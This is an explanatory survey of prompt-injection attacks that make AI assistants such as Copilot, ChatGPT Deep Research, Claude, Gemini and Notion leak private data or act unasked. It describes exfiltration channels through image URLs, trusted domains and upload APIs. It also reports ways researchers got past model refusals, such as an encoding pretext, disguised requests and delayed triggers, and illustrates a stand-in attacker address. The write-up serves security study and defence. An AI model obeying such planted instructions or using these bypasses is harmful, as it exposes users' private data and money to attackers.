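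The instruction was in a hidden comment in the description of a pull request, which is a proposed change to somebody's code. GitHub allows hidden comments there, and Copilot Chat read them. Copilot Chat also had the permissions of the user asking, including access to that user's private code. In the demonstrations, the researcher obtained the description of an undisclosed software vulnerability from a private project, and the results of a search for cloud-service keys.

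By 14 August 2025, GitHub had disabled all images in Copilot Chat to fix the flaw. A year earlier, it had closed a simpler version of the leak in the VS Code editor by blocking images from untrusted domains (Willison, 2024). That block would not have stopped CamoLeak, because every image in the attack came from GitHub's own domain.

### OpenAI's first check and AgentFlayer

OpenAI left the picture leak unfixed for most of 2023. In December it added a check called url_safe, which Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* examines. Before displaying a picture, ChatGPT's web page sent the picture's address to OpenAI's server to check whether it was safe. OpenAI didn't publish the criteria. Rehberger tried 36 pictures on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and ChatGPT displayed nine of them, so an attacker could still leak some text one character at a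 time. The check ran only in the web version, so the iPhone app remained open to the original attack.

Rehberger reported more ways around the check in October 2024. Some still worked in 2025, according to Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*.

By then ChatGPT had connectors, so a successful injection could reach data outside the current conversation. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes an attack in which the victim uploads a document containing an instruction in tiny white type and asks for a summary. ChatGPT skips the summary and searches the victim's Google Drive for API keys, the passwords that programs use to access online services. Its reply then includes an image whose address contains the keys.

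This attack took data from the connector and sent it out in the address of an image. At first url_safe blocked the image because its address belonged to an unfamiliar site. The researchers then moved the image to Azure Blob, Microsoft's storage service, which url_safe accepted. Anyone can rent storage there and have Microsoft log every request for a file, including the text after the question mark in the address. Zenity Labs calls the attack "0click", meaning that the victim clicks nothing after uploading the document. The attacker still has to get the document to the victim, and the victim has to upload it.

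### Checks that come too late

A check on pictures is useful only if it finishes before the browser sends the request. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes an attack on the assistant in Notion, a program for shared documents, in which a user uploads a job applicant's résumé and asks for help updating a table of candidates. Hidden text in the résumé makes the assistant insert a picture into the table's page, with the page's contents in the picture's address. Notion asked the user whether to trust the outside site, but by then it had saved the edit and the browser had requested the picture. The attacker therefore received salary expectations and notes on candidates even if the user refused.

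PromptArmor reported this on 24 December 2025 through HackerOne, a company that handles vulnerability reports for other organizations. HackerOne's staff closed the report as "Not Applicable" before it reached Notion. PromptArmor published its findings on 7 January 2026, and Notion released a fix that night.

SearchLeak also depended on timing. Copilot displays an answer while the model is still writing it, so the browser requested the image before Microsoft's software had cleaned up the answer and made it harmless.

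### When the agent sends the data itself

Image controls don't prevent leaks when an agent can open web pages on its own. Radware's *ShadowLeak* shows this with Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that spends up to half an hour reading sources and writing a report. Those sources can include private mail if the user connects Gmail.

In Radware's demonstration, an attacker sends an email that looks like a routine message about a company restructuring. The mailbox also contains a genuine message with an employee's name and address. When the user asks Deep Research to examine the day's mail, it reads both messages and follows the instruction in the attacker's email to copy the personal details, encode them and open a web address that contains them. The user sees no picture, link or request for approval.

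Radware's researchers needed several attempts. Deep Research recognised an open request to send personal data elsewhere as malicious. It also treated the attacker's address as suspicious and searched for it online instead of opening it. The agent displayed some of its reasoning, which helped the researchers work out what was blocking the attack. Telling it to use a particular browsing tool and retry after failures sometimes worked, but it often left out the personal data. The researchers overcame the last obstacle by having the model encode the data first, on the pretext that this protected it. According to Radware, the software behind the browsing tool then received only a meaningless string. The final version of the attack worked every time in repeated tests, though Radware doesn't say how many it ran.

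The request came from OpenAI's servers, so OpenAI's restrictions on images in the user's browser did not apply to it. Radware found no comparable limit on the addresses Deep Research could open. Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI had fixed it by early August and acknowledged it on 3 September.

Other agents had similar channels. Superhuman's assistant could look up news on the web, and PromptArmor found that a planted instruction could make it open a web address containing the user's mail. A strict image policy would therefore have closed only one of Superhuman's leaks. Willison's *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents* describes an attack in which a PDF made Notion's agent put client names and revenue into a web address and pass it to its web search tool. This happened in September 2025, months before the image leak in the same product. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity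 Exfiltrates Data* reports that attackers could steal credentials through Google's code editor because its main agent can direct a second agent that operates a browser.

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often one such agent leaked a secret. The researchers put instructions in the titles and descriptions of web pages, which the agent fetched automatically to preview a link. The user asked only for a summary. Over 480 runs, the agent sent the secret to the researchers' server about 89 per cent of the time. Checks on the final answer missed 95 per cent of the successful attacks, since the answer was usually a harmless summary. The model had only 7 billion parameters and the secret was already in its context window, so the leak rate is weak evidence about commercial products. But checking answers should still have the same weakness with larger models, because an agent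 can leak data through a tool without showing it in the answer.

Lan and colleagues found that restricting which domains the agent could contact and following redirects to their final destination worked considerably better than adding defensive instructions to the prompt, which helped little.

### Allowing only addresses that already exist

In *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), OpenAI argues that even a good list of trusted domains is inadequate for an agent that browses the web, because trusted sites can redirect to other sites and a short list would exclude many legitimate ones. Frequent warnings might also train people to click through them.

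OpenAI instead checks the exact address. It runs a crawler that records public web addresses without access to anyone's conversations. If the crawler has already recorded an address, ChatGPT can fetch it automatically. Otherwise the agent must try another site, or the user gets a warning that the address may contain information from the conversation. OpenAI reasons that an address that existed independently of a conversation is unlikely to contain secrets from it. In the door-code example, the crawler would probably have recorded attacker.example/logo.png, but not the version ending in 4471. OpenAI applies the same check to page visits in its Atlas browser and to searches and page visits in Deep Research, the channel used in ShadowLeak.

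CamoLeak shows that an agent can still leak information by choosing among addresses that are all public. If an attacker's site has *n* known pages and the agent opens one of them, the choice conveys up to log₂ *n* bits. With 1,000 pages, one visit can stand for any three-digit number, so two visits could convey a six-digit login code. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* notes that OpenAI acknowledges this gap. Stealing a mailbox this way would take a very large number of requests, which might arrive out of order. Rehberger suggests stopping an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, which would make it even harder to spell out ordinary text.

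Rehberger also worries that some of OpenAI's own developers may not know about the check or use it. The company has many products, and an address check may not cover a product where the model can run code. In May 2026, PromptArmor told OpenAI about a flaw in ChatGPT for Google Sheets, where the model can run privileged scripts. PromptArmor followed up several times but received only an automated reply.

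### Uploads to the attacker's own account

Anthropic restricts where Claude can send data when it runs code. The code runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment. In October 2025, the default setting allowed connections only to a short list of domains, mostly services that programmers download software from. The list also included Anthropic's API, which programs use to access Claude.

Anthropic's API accepts file uploads from any customer with a valid key, including an attacker. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes a document that makes Claude save the user's last conversation to a file and upload it with the attacker's key, which puts the file in the attacker's account. Each upload can be up to 30 megabytes, far more than a web address can hold. The attack worked the first time Rehberger tried it. Claude then refused for a long while, treating the key in the document as suspicious,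 until Rehberger disguised the request.

The allow-list worked as Anthropic had configured it, since Claude contacted only an approved domain. But the domain doesn't identify who will receive the data. Rehberger proposes limiting the sandbox's connections to the logged-in user's account, which would remove this channel without cutting Claude off from the API.

Rehberger reported the problem on 25 October 2025, and the report was closed within an hour as a model safety issue outside the scope of Anthropic's bug programme. Five days later, the company said that such leaks were in scope and that closing the report had been a mistake in its process.

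The channel was still open in January 2026, when Anthropic released Cowork, an agent for everyday office work that can read folders on the user's computer. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed the same kind of upload in Cowork. The test user gave Cowork a folder of property files, then uploaded a Word document that supposedly contained instructions for analysing them. Cowork followed hidden text in the document and, without asking for approval, uploaded the largest file it could find, a loan estimate with financial figures and partial social security numbers.

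That test used Haiku, a smaller Claude model. In a different scenario, PromptArmor got the more resistant Opus 4.5 to leak customer records through the same channel. Anthropic acknowledged the risk and said it was updating Cowork's virtual machine, according to TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection*.

### Who could have seen the data leave

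The researchers published few logs from the victims' side, but where a request starts largely determines who can record it.

| Leak | User | Employer | Vendor |
|---|---|---|---|
| Superhuman, by picture | The full address, in the browser's network log | A request to Google Docs | The address, in the model's answer |
| CamoLeak | Invisible pixels, and a series of requests in the network log | Requests to GitHub's picture server | Camo's requests to an outside server, one per character |
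| ShadowLeak | Nothing on screen | Nothing | The agent's tool call and the request from OpenAI's servers |
| Cowork | The upload command, after expanding a collapsed block | At most, traffic to Anthropic | An upload with another customer's key |

Users were the least likely to notice data theft in time. PromptArmor found the stolen emails in the test user's network log, but hardly anyone opens that log during normal use. Anthropic advised Cowork users to watch for suspicious actions that might indicate prompt injection. PromptArmor quotes Willison, who thought it unfair to ask this of non-programmers. It also seems a lot to expect of people who delegated a task so they wouldn't have to do it themselves.

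An employer can monitor traffic from its staff's computers and might notice an image request to an unknown domain. But requests to Google or GitHub look like ordinary work, and because web traffic is encrypted, the employer would have to decrypt it to see what an address contained. ShadowLeak bypassed the employer's network. Radware recommends monitoring whether an agent's actions match the user's goal, and it sells this kind of protection.

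Vendors could see the most in all four cases. Anthropic could, in principle, have compared the account receiving a file with the account of the user whose session sent it. Rehberger pointed out in 2023 that url_safe gave OpenAI a record of every image address it checked, and that a run of single-letter images would stand out in it. Attackers can make such records harder to interpret by splitting a secret across several requests. When Lan and colleagues did this, their measure of leakage in any single request fell by 73 per cent, and the pieces got past simple filters that look for sensitive strings.

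Even reading logs can leak data. Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) reports that OpenAI's log viewer for developers displayed Markdown images. A developer's product might block a malicious answer before the user saw it, but OpenAI still logged the answer. When the developer opened the log to investigate, their browser fetched the image and sent private data to the attacker.

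## Zero-click attacks on workplace assistants

Many of the thefts described so far began when the victim uploaded the attacker's document or asked about the attacker's page. An enterprise copilot can search an organisation's mail, chats and documents on behalf of an employee, and it selects what to read. An attacker can therefore send an email and wait for the copilot to retrieve it, in what researchers call a zero-click attack.

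The term "zero-click" is older than AI assistants. In phone security it describes an attack that succeeds as soon as a phone receives a message, even if the owner never touches the phone. For assistants it has a looser meaning: the victim does nothing beyond using the assistant normally. The victim usually asks the assistant a question, but doesn't open the attacker's message, click a link or approve an action.

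### How a stranger's email ends up beside confidential files

A language model's training data doesn't include last week's meetings, so a workplace copilot looks up relevant material before it answers, a method called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how Microsoft 365 Copilot does this. When an employee asks a question, Copilot queries Microsoft Graph, the service through which programs access an organisation's data. It then adds relevant passages from the employee's mailbox, stored files, internal websites and Teams chats to the context window with the question.

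Such searches often go by meaning instead of exact words. A separate model, the embedder, turns each passage into a vector, a long list of numbers, and passages with similar meanings get vectors that point in similar directions. The software also turns the question into a vector and picks the passages whose vectors are closest to it. A common measure of closeness is the cosine of the angle between two vectors, cos θ = (a · b) / (|a| |b|), which is 1 when they point the same way and 0 when they are at right angles. Microsoft hasn't published how Copilot's search works, so Ravia is assuming that it works something like this.

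Copilot retrieves only what the employee is allowed to read, but that includes emails from anyone. If a stranger's message and a confidential salary table both seem relevant to a question about pay, both go into the context window. The permissions don't prevent the stranger's text from influencing the answer.

### EchoLeak

Ravia's team at Aim Labs, the research department of Aim Security, turned this into an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot and named it EchoLeak. The team contacted Microsoft in January 2025, Microsoft finished the patch in May, and Aim published its findings on 11 June, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. The flaw is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. TechRepublic's *First Known Zero-Click AI Exploit* reports that Microsoft rated it critical, with a score of 9.3 out of 10 on CVSS, the standard severity scale.

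The attack starts with an email to an employee. Microsoft has a classifier meant to catch planted instructions before they reach the model, but the researchers worded the email so that the classifier labeled it as ordinary correspondence. Ravia thinks such classifiers are hard to train because good collections of real injections are scarce.

Copilot then has to retrieve the email. A short message about one subject has one vector and is retrieved only for questions close to that subject, so the researchers wanted a long message that the search software would cut into many pieces, each with its own vector. One idea was to repeat the instruction with random misspellings. A language model can still read misspelled text, but the embedder may give it a very different vector. With one of OpenAI's embedders, the similarity between a text and its misspelled copy fell as low as 0.7, less than the similarity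 between a phrase about greeting cards and one about the philosophy of science.

The researchers didn't know which embedding model Microsoft used, so they couldn't tailor the copies to it. They used a simpler method, repeating the instruction under headings about topics employees often ask about, such as parental or other leave. Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics, though Ravia doesn't say how often.

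Once in the context window, the instruction made Copilot pick out the most sensitive information there and add it to a web address on the attacker's server. Microsoft's filter removes links to outside sites from Copilot's answers, but it didn't recognise one of Markdown's two link formats, which puts a short label after the link's text and the address on a separate line. The attack worked, but only if the employee clicked the link. The filter had the same gap for pictures, so the researchers used a picture instead, which needed no click.

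The browser still loaded pictures only from domains on Microsoft's allow-list, so the researchers searched those domains for a service that would forward a request to an attacker's server. They found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for internal websites, but the victim would have had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. A service on the Teams domain had no such requirement. The browser requested the picture from Teams, which then requested it from the attacker's server, using an address that contained the secret.

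Copilot normally cites the documents it used for an answer, but the researchers also got it to leave the malicious email out of those citations. An employee who noticed something odd would therefore have had trouble finding the cause.

According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that EchoLeak had affected no customers, and Aim knew of no victims either. Microsoft is in a good position to know because the requests went through its servers, but outsiders cannot check this.

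Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click vulnerability in a major AI application. Zenity Labs' *EchoLeak* disputes that it was new, saying the attack path had been public for almost a year. Ravia's narrower claim is easier to defend. He says earlier attacks either needed the user to direct the chatbot to a malicious source or could extract only very limited data, and EchoLeak had neither restriction.

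### Whether a question counts as an action

TechRadar's *Microsoft Copilot targeted in first “zero-click” attack on an AI agent* hedged the label by adding "(almost)" to its claim that EchoLeak needed no user interaction. The hedge is fair, because the attack works only if the employee asks Copilot a question close enough to one of the topics in the email. The attacker can't choose when that happens, and an employee who never uses Copilot is safe from this attack. A phone attack that works as soon as the message is delivered has none of these limits.

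The security company Varonis uses this point to contrast a later attack of its own with EchoLeak (Taler, 2026, *Reprompt*). In the Varonis attack, the victim only clicks a link and never has to type a prompt. Both attacks still need one action from the victim, a question for EchoLeak and a click for the Varonis attack.

It seems more useful to define "zero-click" as meaning that the attacker doesn't have to trick the victim into doing anything. EchoLeak fits this definition because employees put questions to Copilot for their own reasons. Ravia knew of no user behaviour or administrator's setting that could have prevented it. A malicious link, by contrast, has to reach the victim and look worth clicking, and companies train their staff to be suspicious of such links. AgentFlayer is a doubtful case because the victim had to upload the attacker's document.

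It is unclear whether some attacks count as zero-click. Willison (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, describes a Microsoft agent that could email its own user without asking for approval. Those emails could contain external images, so data could leak when the user opened the message. The attacker causes the email to be sent, but it comes from the user's own assistant, so most people would open it without hesitation.

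### "LLM scope violation" and the confused deputy

Aim Labs coined the term "LLM scope violation" for what it considers the core of EchoLeak. Ravia defines it as a situation in which an attacker's instructions in untrusted input make the model attend to trusted data in its context without the user's explicit consent. In EchoLeak, an email from outside the company made the model draw on information from inside it.

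Ravia compares this to an unprivileged Unix program that reaches protected files through another program with higher privileges. The more privileged program is a confused deputy, like Hardy's compiler. Willison doesn't think the pattern is new or needs a name, since models have never been able to take account of where their tokens came from.

Ravia argues that a name for scope violations might help people build detectors that look for outside text drawing on inside data. That is a better target than suspicious wording, which an attacker can always change. The precedent is the buffer overflow, an error in which a program writes more data into a piece of memory than it can hold. Engineers gave a separate name to overflows in one region of memory, the stack, and built a specific defence, a marker value that changes if data spills over it. Aim also had a commercial interest in the new term, since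 it had developed a detector for scope violations.

The term also points to a limit of Hardy's remedy, a separate permission for each file. Copilot had already properly fetched the confidential passages to answer the employee's own question. The model didn't need to open anything else to follow the attacker's instruction, so a permission check at that point would not have stopped it. The software would have to track where each passage came from and restrict what the model could do with it. In *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) recommend such defences, including dividing the prompt into parts and basing access rules on a text's origin.

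The phrase "explicit consent" makes Ravia's definition difficult to apply. An employee who asks Copilot to compare a supplier's emailed quotation with the internal budget wants it to combine outside and internal data. To distinguish this request from an attack, a detector would need information about what the employee meant to ask for. "LLM scope violation" is probably best understood as a kind of confused deputy problem in which the deputy already holds the confidential data when it reads the attacker's instruction.

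### Customer records and company search

EchoLeak depended on several oversights in Microsoft's software, but the security company Noma found two similar attacks on other vendors' products the same year.

ForcedLeak affected Agentforce, a platform for building AI agents that work with a company's Salesforce customer records. The Hacker News (2025) reports that it had a CVSS score of 9.4 and affected organisations that used Agentforce with Web-to-Lead, a feature that turns enquiries from a company's website form into sales leads. An attacker could fill in the form like any prospective customer. According to Varonis' *ForcedLeak and the Future of AI Agent Security*, the form's description field holds up to 42,000 characters, more than enough for a planted instruction.

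The instruction then stayed in the customer database until an employee asked the agent about the lead. Willison (2025), in *ForcedLeak*, explains that the instruction made the agent collect leads' email addresses and put them in the URL of an image. The attack resembles EchoLeak, but EchoLeak arrived by email, and a company can treat email from outside senders with more suspicion. The form entry was already a record in the company's own database when the agent read it.

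Salesforce's allow-list should have stopped the browser from loading the picture, but it still included my-salesforce-cms.com, a domain whose registration had expired. BeyondMachines reports that Noma's researchers bought the domain for $5. Because an allow-list identifies domains by name, a domain stays trusted after its owner changes unless someone removes it from the list. Noma could therefore receive the data directly, whereas in EchoLeak, Aim had to find a Microsoft service that would forward a request.

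Salesforce recovered the domain and began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for its agents, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed*. Recovering the domain stopped only the abuse of that one address, but enforcing the list also protects against addresses that no one has abused yet, as long as someone keeps it up to date. There are no public reports of criminals using ForcedLeak.

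Noma's other attack, GeminiJack, affected Gemini Enterprise, Google's AI assistants for companies, and Vertex AI Search, a Google platform for building search tools. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* reports that Noma discovered it in June 2025 and told Google the same day. The attacker shared a document or sent an email or calendar invitation that contained instructions. When an employee ran a search that retrieved the item, Gemini followed the instructions, and an image request then carried the results to the attacker.

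SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data* says that the attack needed no user interaction, while SC Media's *Google addresses 'GeminiJack' exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* specifies that a routine search triggered it. Noma called GeminiJack an architectural weakness, and its resemblance to EchoLeak supports that. Google and Microsoft built their search systems separately, but both systems put outsiders' text in the same context window as company data and allowed the answer to load an image. Google has fixed the flaw, and as with ForcedLeak, nobody has publicly reported an actual data theft.

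### Links that ask the question for the user

Varonis found a way to attack Copilot without waiting for an employee to ask a question. A link to Copilot can include a question in the "q" parameter of its address, and when someone opens the link, Copilot answers as though that person had typed the question. This is convenient for bookmarks and shortcuts, but an attacker can also write the question.

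Reprompt, the first of these attacks, worked on Copilot Personal, the consumer version. Clicking the link sent the attacker the victim's name, location and details of events mentioned in their Copilot history, according to Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026). The attack kept running after the victim closed the chat. Microsoft had fixed the flaw by the time Ars Technica reported it on 14 January 2026, and the only attackers the article describes are Varonis' own researchers.

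Varonis then tried the same kind of link on the search function of Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise and was surprised that it worked. The resulting attack, SearchLeak, sent data out through Bing before Microsoft's software had cleaned up the answer. In the demonstration, Copilot searched the victim's mail and leaked the subject line of one message. Such a leak can be harmful because many services put login codes in their subject lines. Varonis published the attack on 15 June 2026, after Microsoft had patched the flaw, and mentions no real victims.

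Neither attack is zero-click, because the attacker has to get somebody to follow a link. But the link leads to a genuine Microsoft site, so checking the domain before clicking doesn't help, and Varonis notes that tools for blocking phishing links let it through. Varonis says that Microsoft gave SearchLeak its highest severity rating, critical. But Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reports that Microsoft gave it a CVSS score of only 6.5, or medium, partly because it requires user interaction. EchoLeak, which could reach much the same data, scored 9.3.

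It is also hard to say whether these are indirect injections. The attacker wrote the instruction, and it works against a user who doesn't know what it says, as in the copy-and-paste trick that Greshake and colleagues mention. But Copilot received the instruction as the user's own request, as it would a direct injection, rather than finding it in a page or email.

Training a model to prioritise the user's messages over retrieved text would, if anything, make this attack easier. An ordinary software fix would be for Copilot to put the question from the link into the text box and wait for the user to press Enter. Web developers have long dealt with a similar problem, cross-site request forgery, in which one website makes a visitor's browser send commands to another site where the visitor is logged in.

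A third attack of this kind, CoSnitch, became public in August 2026. It affected Copilot Personal when users had connected it to services such as Gmail, Outlook or Google Drive. Techlicious reports that one click on a crafted link ran a hidden command with all the access the user had given Copilot. Varonis showed Copilot retrieving calendar details, file names and whole emails, including passwords typed into them. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* adds that the attack also planted false entries in Copilot's persistent memory. Varonis had reported the flaw in December 2025, and Microsoft released the final fix on 18 August. Both accounts describe what the researchers did, and neither names a real victim.

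### ReLeak

The team behind EchoLeak, now part of the network security company Cato Networks, found three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) announced them on 3 December 2026. Like EchoLeak, each began with an unread email that Copilot retrieved when the employee asked an ordinary question. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft's defences against planted instructions stopped none of them.

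The three attacks sent data out in different ways. In one, Copilot put the data in an image URL and Bing fetched the image, much as in SearchLeak. In another, Copilot saved an Office or PDF file containing a link with the data in it, and Microsoft's background software sent the data out when it processed the file. The third used Copilot's tool for running Python code. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) notes that Microsoft documented this tool as unable to send traffic out, but the researchers found a way around the block. Microsoft rated that flaw critical.

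Two of these routes came with Copilot's newer abilities to write files and run code. The route through Bing is harder to excuse. Ravia had published Copilot's whole allow-list, including Bing's domains, in June 2025. Varonis showed a year later that Bing would forward data to an attacker, and Microsoft patched SearchLeak. Cato reported another Bing attack after that, between late July and 20 August 2026, so the patch must have left some way through. Microsoft fixed the Bing route on 15 November, after the other two. Cato knows of no real attack that used any of the three.

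## Unwanted actions through email, calendars, payments and devices

An injected action is one that the user's account is permitted to take but that the user did not ask for. In one of OpenAI's own tests, a planted email made an agent send its user's resignation when the user wanted an out-of-office reply. To make an assistant delete a meeting or send a payment, an attacker needs only a tool that can do it, whereas stealing data requires a channel to leak it through. Researchers have produced most of the known cases in simulations or on their own accounts. The clearest loss to anyone else is a cryptocurrency theft in May 2026.

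Permission checks miss injected actions because the assistant carries out a stranger's instructions with its user's login, which makes it a "confused deputy". If a homeowner has connected an assistant to the windows, the smart-home service accepts its command to open them, even when a stranger's email prompted it. An allow-list of web addresses doesn't help either, because the request goes to a service the user connected on purpose.

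Mailboxes and calendars are good places to plant instructions because anyone who knows the address can write to them. Google Calendar users can accept invitations from everyone, only from known senders, or only after responding by email. Nassi, Cohen and Yair (2025) argue in *Invitation Is All You Need!* that most people probably keep the default. Google warns that the "known senders" setting may reveal to senders that they are not in the user's contacts, which could discourage people from using it. The setting also doesn't stop an attacker the user knows, such as a boss, a colleague or a former friend. Users may not see the invitation either, because Calendar lists five events before a "Show more" button. A sixth can stay hidden while Gemini still reads it, according to Daily Security Review's *Google Calendar Invites Let Researchers Hijack Gemini in Stealthy Prompt-Injection Attack*.

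### Calendar invitations against Gemini

Nassi and colleagues attacked three versions of Google's assistant: the Gemini website, the Gemini phone app and Google Assistant. They usually put the planted instruction in the title of a calendar invitation. When the user asked about the week's events, Gemini loaded the titles, including the instruction, into its context window. The researchers sorted the attacks into five classes and rated the risk of each outcome.

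| Class | Outcome | Risk before Google's changes |
|---|---|---|
| Short-term context poisoning | The assistant reads out abuse and a false medical result, promotes an investment, or offers a phishing link | High, medium and very high |
| Long-term memory poisoning | False information stays in the assistant's memory for later conversations | Low |
| Tool misuse | The calendar agent deletes or adds events | Medium |
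| Automatic agent invocation | The smart-home agent opens windows, starts the boiler, or switches lights | Critical for windows, high for the others |
| Automatic app invocation | The phone streams video through Zoom, leaks emails or meeting titles, reveals its location, or downloads a file | Critical for video and emails, very high for meetings, high for location, medium for the download |

The paper counts 14 attacks, including a worm that it rates critical. The researchers did not repeat the memory attack, which Rehberger had already shown, and they describe the worm as something an attacker could build from the email theft. They ran the other attacks on their own accounts. The windows and boiler were in a flat that they controlled and may have prepared for the purpose. The app attacks worked only on Android.

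The attack that opened a window from a calendar entry had to get around two restrictions in Gemini. Gemini's main model, called the orchestrator, plans the work and calls specialised agents for the calendar, email or smart home. The calendar agent cannot call the smart-home agent and can only return its output to the orchestrator. Google had also stopped Gemini from using its more sensitive tools in the same turn as it read outside content.

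Rehberger had run into that second barrier in November 2023. A planted instruction could make Gemini, then called Bard, search for flights and hotels, but not open the user's documents. Embrace The Red's *Google Gemini* describes how he got past it with an email that told Gemini to wait until the user's next request before fetching a document. By then the block had lapsed, but the email was still in the context window, and Gemini fetched a document about cats from his Google Drive.

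Nassi and colleagues wrote invitations that instructed Gemini to wait until the user typed something like "thank you" before acting. The user asked about upcoming events, Gemini listed them, the user thanked it, and the boiler came on. The researchers call this a "1/2-click" attack because the victim has to do something, but only something that people do several times a day. *The Promptware Kill Chain* (2026), which analyses the Zoom version, notes that the attack depends on Gemini retrieving the invitation, which is not guaranteed.

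The researchers rated the threats using an adapted version of a standard that carmakers use for cyber risks. A threat's impact is the worst of its financial, operational, safety and privacy effects. The open window counts as critical because somebody could photograph the resident through it. Likelihood is the average of six factors, such as the equipment and skill an attacker needs. Nearly all the attacks scored "very likely" because a computer science graduate with a laptop and the victim's email address could prepare one in less than a day. The ratings are structured opinions about what could happen, and the researchers did not count how often such attacks occur.

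Google received the report on 22 February 2025 and changed Gemini before the paper came out that August. It extended confirmation prompts to risky operations on a user's Google data, across apps and on devices. It also improved its removal of suspicious links and added a classifier to filter out planted instructions. Google then reran the researchers' prompts, with variations, to check the defences. In its statement, Google called the scenarios "theoretical", although the researchers had filmed the attacks on the working product.

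In January 2026 the security company Miggo disclosed an attack that leaked private meeting details through the calendar itself. According to The Hacker News (2026), the attacker put an instruction in an invitation's description. When the user later asked Gemini something like whether they had meetings on Tuesday, Gemini summarised the day's meetings, including private ones, wrote the summary into a new event, and gave the user a harmless answer. Under many companies' calendar settings, the attacker could read the new event.

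Miggo told SecurityWeek, in *Weaponized Invite Enabled Calendar Data Theft via Google Gemini*, that the planted text could pass for a user's own request. People ask Gemini to summarise their day and create events, so a filter for suspicious wording had little to detect. Google has fixed the flaw, but the same approach could work with any field that an assistant can write to and an outsider can read.

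### Email that copies itself

Greshake and colleagues ran their 2023 self-forwarding email in a mock application, passing the message and the contact list to the model by hand. A year later, Stav Cohen, Ron Bitton and Ben Nassi built a fuller version called Morris II, named after the Morris worm that spread across the internet in 1988.

*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) explains that the planted text has three parts. One gets the model to follow the planted instructions, another is an instruction to copy the whole text into its output, and the last causes the harm, for example by adding private details to the outgoing email. An assistant that uses retrieval-augmented generation saves the incoming message and retrieves it later while drafting a reply. The reply then contains the planted text, and the recipient's assistant saves it in turn.

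The researchers tested this on 2,000 messages from 20 employees of Enron, the collapsed energy company whose emails became public. In one configuration, about one in five generated messages compromised a new assistant. At that rate, an infected assistant would have to send an average of more than five messages to other assistants like it for the worm to keep spreading. That is not many for a mail assistant, but the figure only holds if the recipients' assistants store and answer mail automatically.

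*Responsible Development of Offensive AI* (2025) reproduced the Morris II attack on Falcon3, an open model released in December 2024. Nobody has reported such a worm on public email systems. *AI Agents Enable Adaptive Computer Worms* (2026) describes a worm that carries its own language model and uses it to work out a new attack on each computer it reaches. It ran in a closed virtual network. Unlike Morris II, which spreads one text among assistants that will obey it, this worm breaks into ordinary machines and doesn't need an assistant to read anything.

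### Spending the user's money

In 2025, Guardio, a company that sells protection against scams, generated a fake Walmart site with one prompt to an AI website builder and told Perplexity's browser Comet to buy an Apple Watch there. Guardio's *Scamlexity* gives no counts but reports that Comet sometimes refused, sometimes left the checkout to the user, and sometimes filled in the saved address and card details and completed the order without asking.

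The shop in this test contained no planted instruction. The user had asked for a watch, and Comet missed clues that the seller was fake, as many people would. Guardio also tested a real injection, PromptFix, with less at stake. A fake message from a doctor's office led Comet to a page with a captcha, a test meant to keep bots out. Hidden text on the page said that the agent could solve this one for its user by clicking a button. Comet clicked it, which downloaded a harmless file. The two tests showed that Comet could pay a scammer and that it could obey hidden text, but not that hidden text could make it pay.

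Planted text has caused cryptocurrency agents to send money in tests. In *Real AI Agents with Fake Memories*, Patlan, Sheng and colleagues (2025) studied ElizaOS, free software for building agents that trade and post on social media. Bots built with it together managed more than $25 million. The researchers gave a bot a wallet and an X account and had it answer replies. The bot followed a request in one reply to transfer 0.001 ether to the writer's account, first on a test network, where the coins are worthless, and then on the main Ethereum network with real funds from its wallet.

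A simple defence stopped that attack. The researchers put tags around text from outside and told the model to treat anything between the tags as data. They then attacked the bot's memory, which the tags did not cover. They write an agent's context at time *t* as

c_t = (p_t, d_t, k, h_t)

where *p* is the user's prompt, *d* is outside data, *k* is fixed background knowledge and *h* is the stored history of earlier conversations. An ordinary indirect injection changes *d*. A memory injection changes *h*, and the instruction can then come back in a later conversation with someone else.

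In one example, Melissa sends a bot on the chat service Discord a message that contains an instruction about where transfers should go and ends with an ordinary question. The bot answers only the question but saves the whole message. Later, Bob asks the same bot, on X, to send some ether. The software retrieves the shared history, and the bot sends Bob's ether to Melissa's address. Bob did ask for a transfer, so only the recipient was injected.

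Patlan and colleagues also built a benchmark with more than 150 blockchain tasks and over 500 attack cases. Warnings in the prompt were not enough to stop the attacks once an attacker had corrupted the stored history. Further training made the attacks much less successful, and the model could still do single-step tasks.

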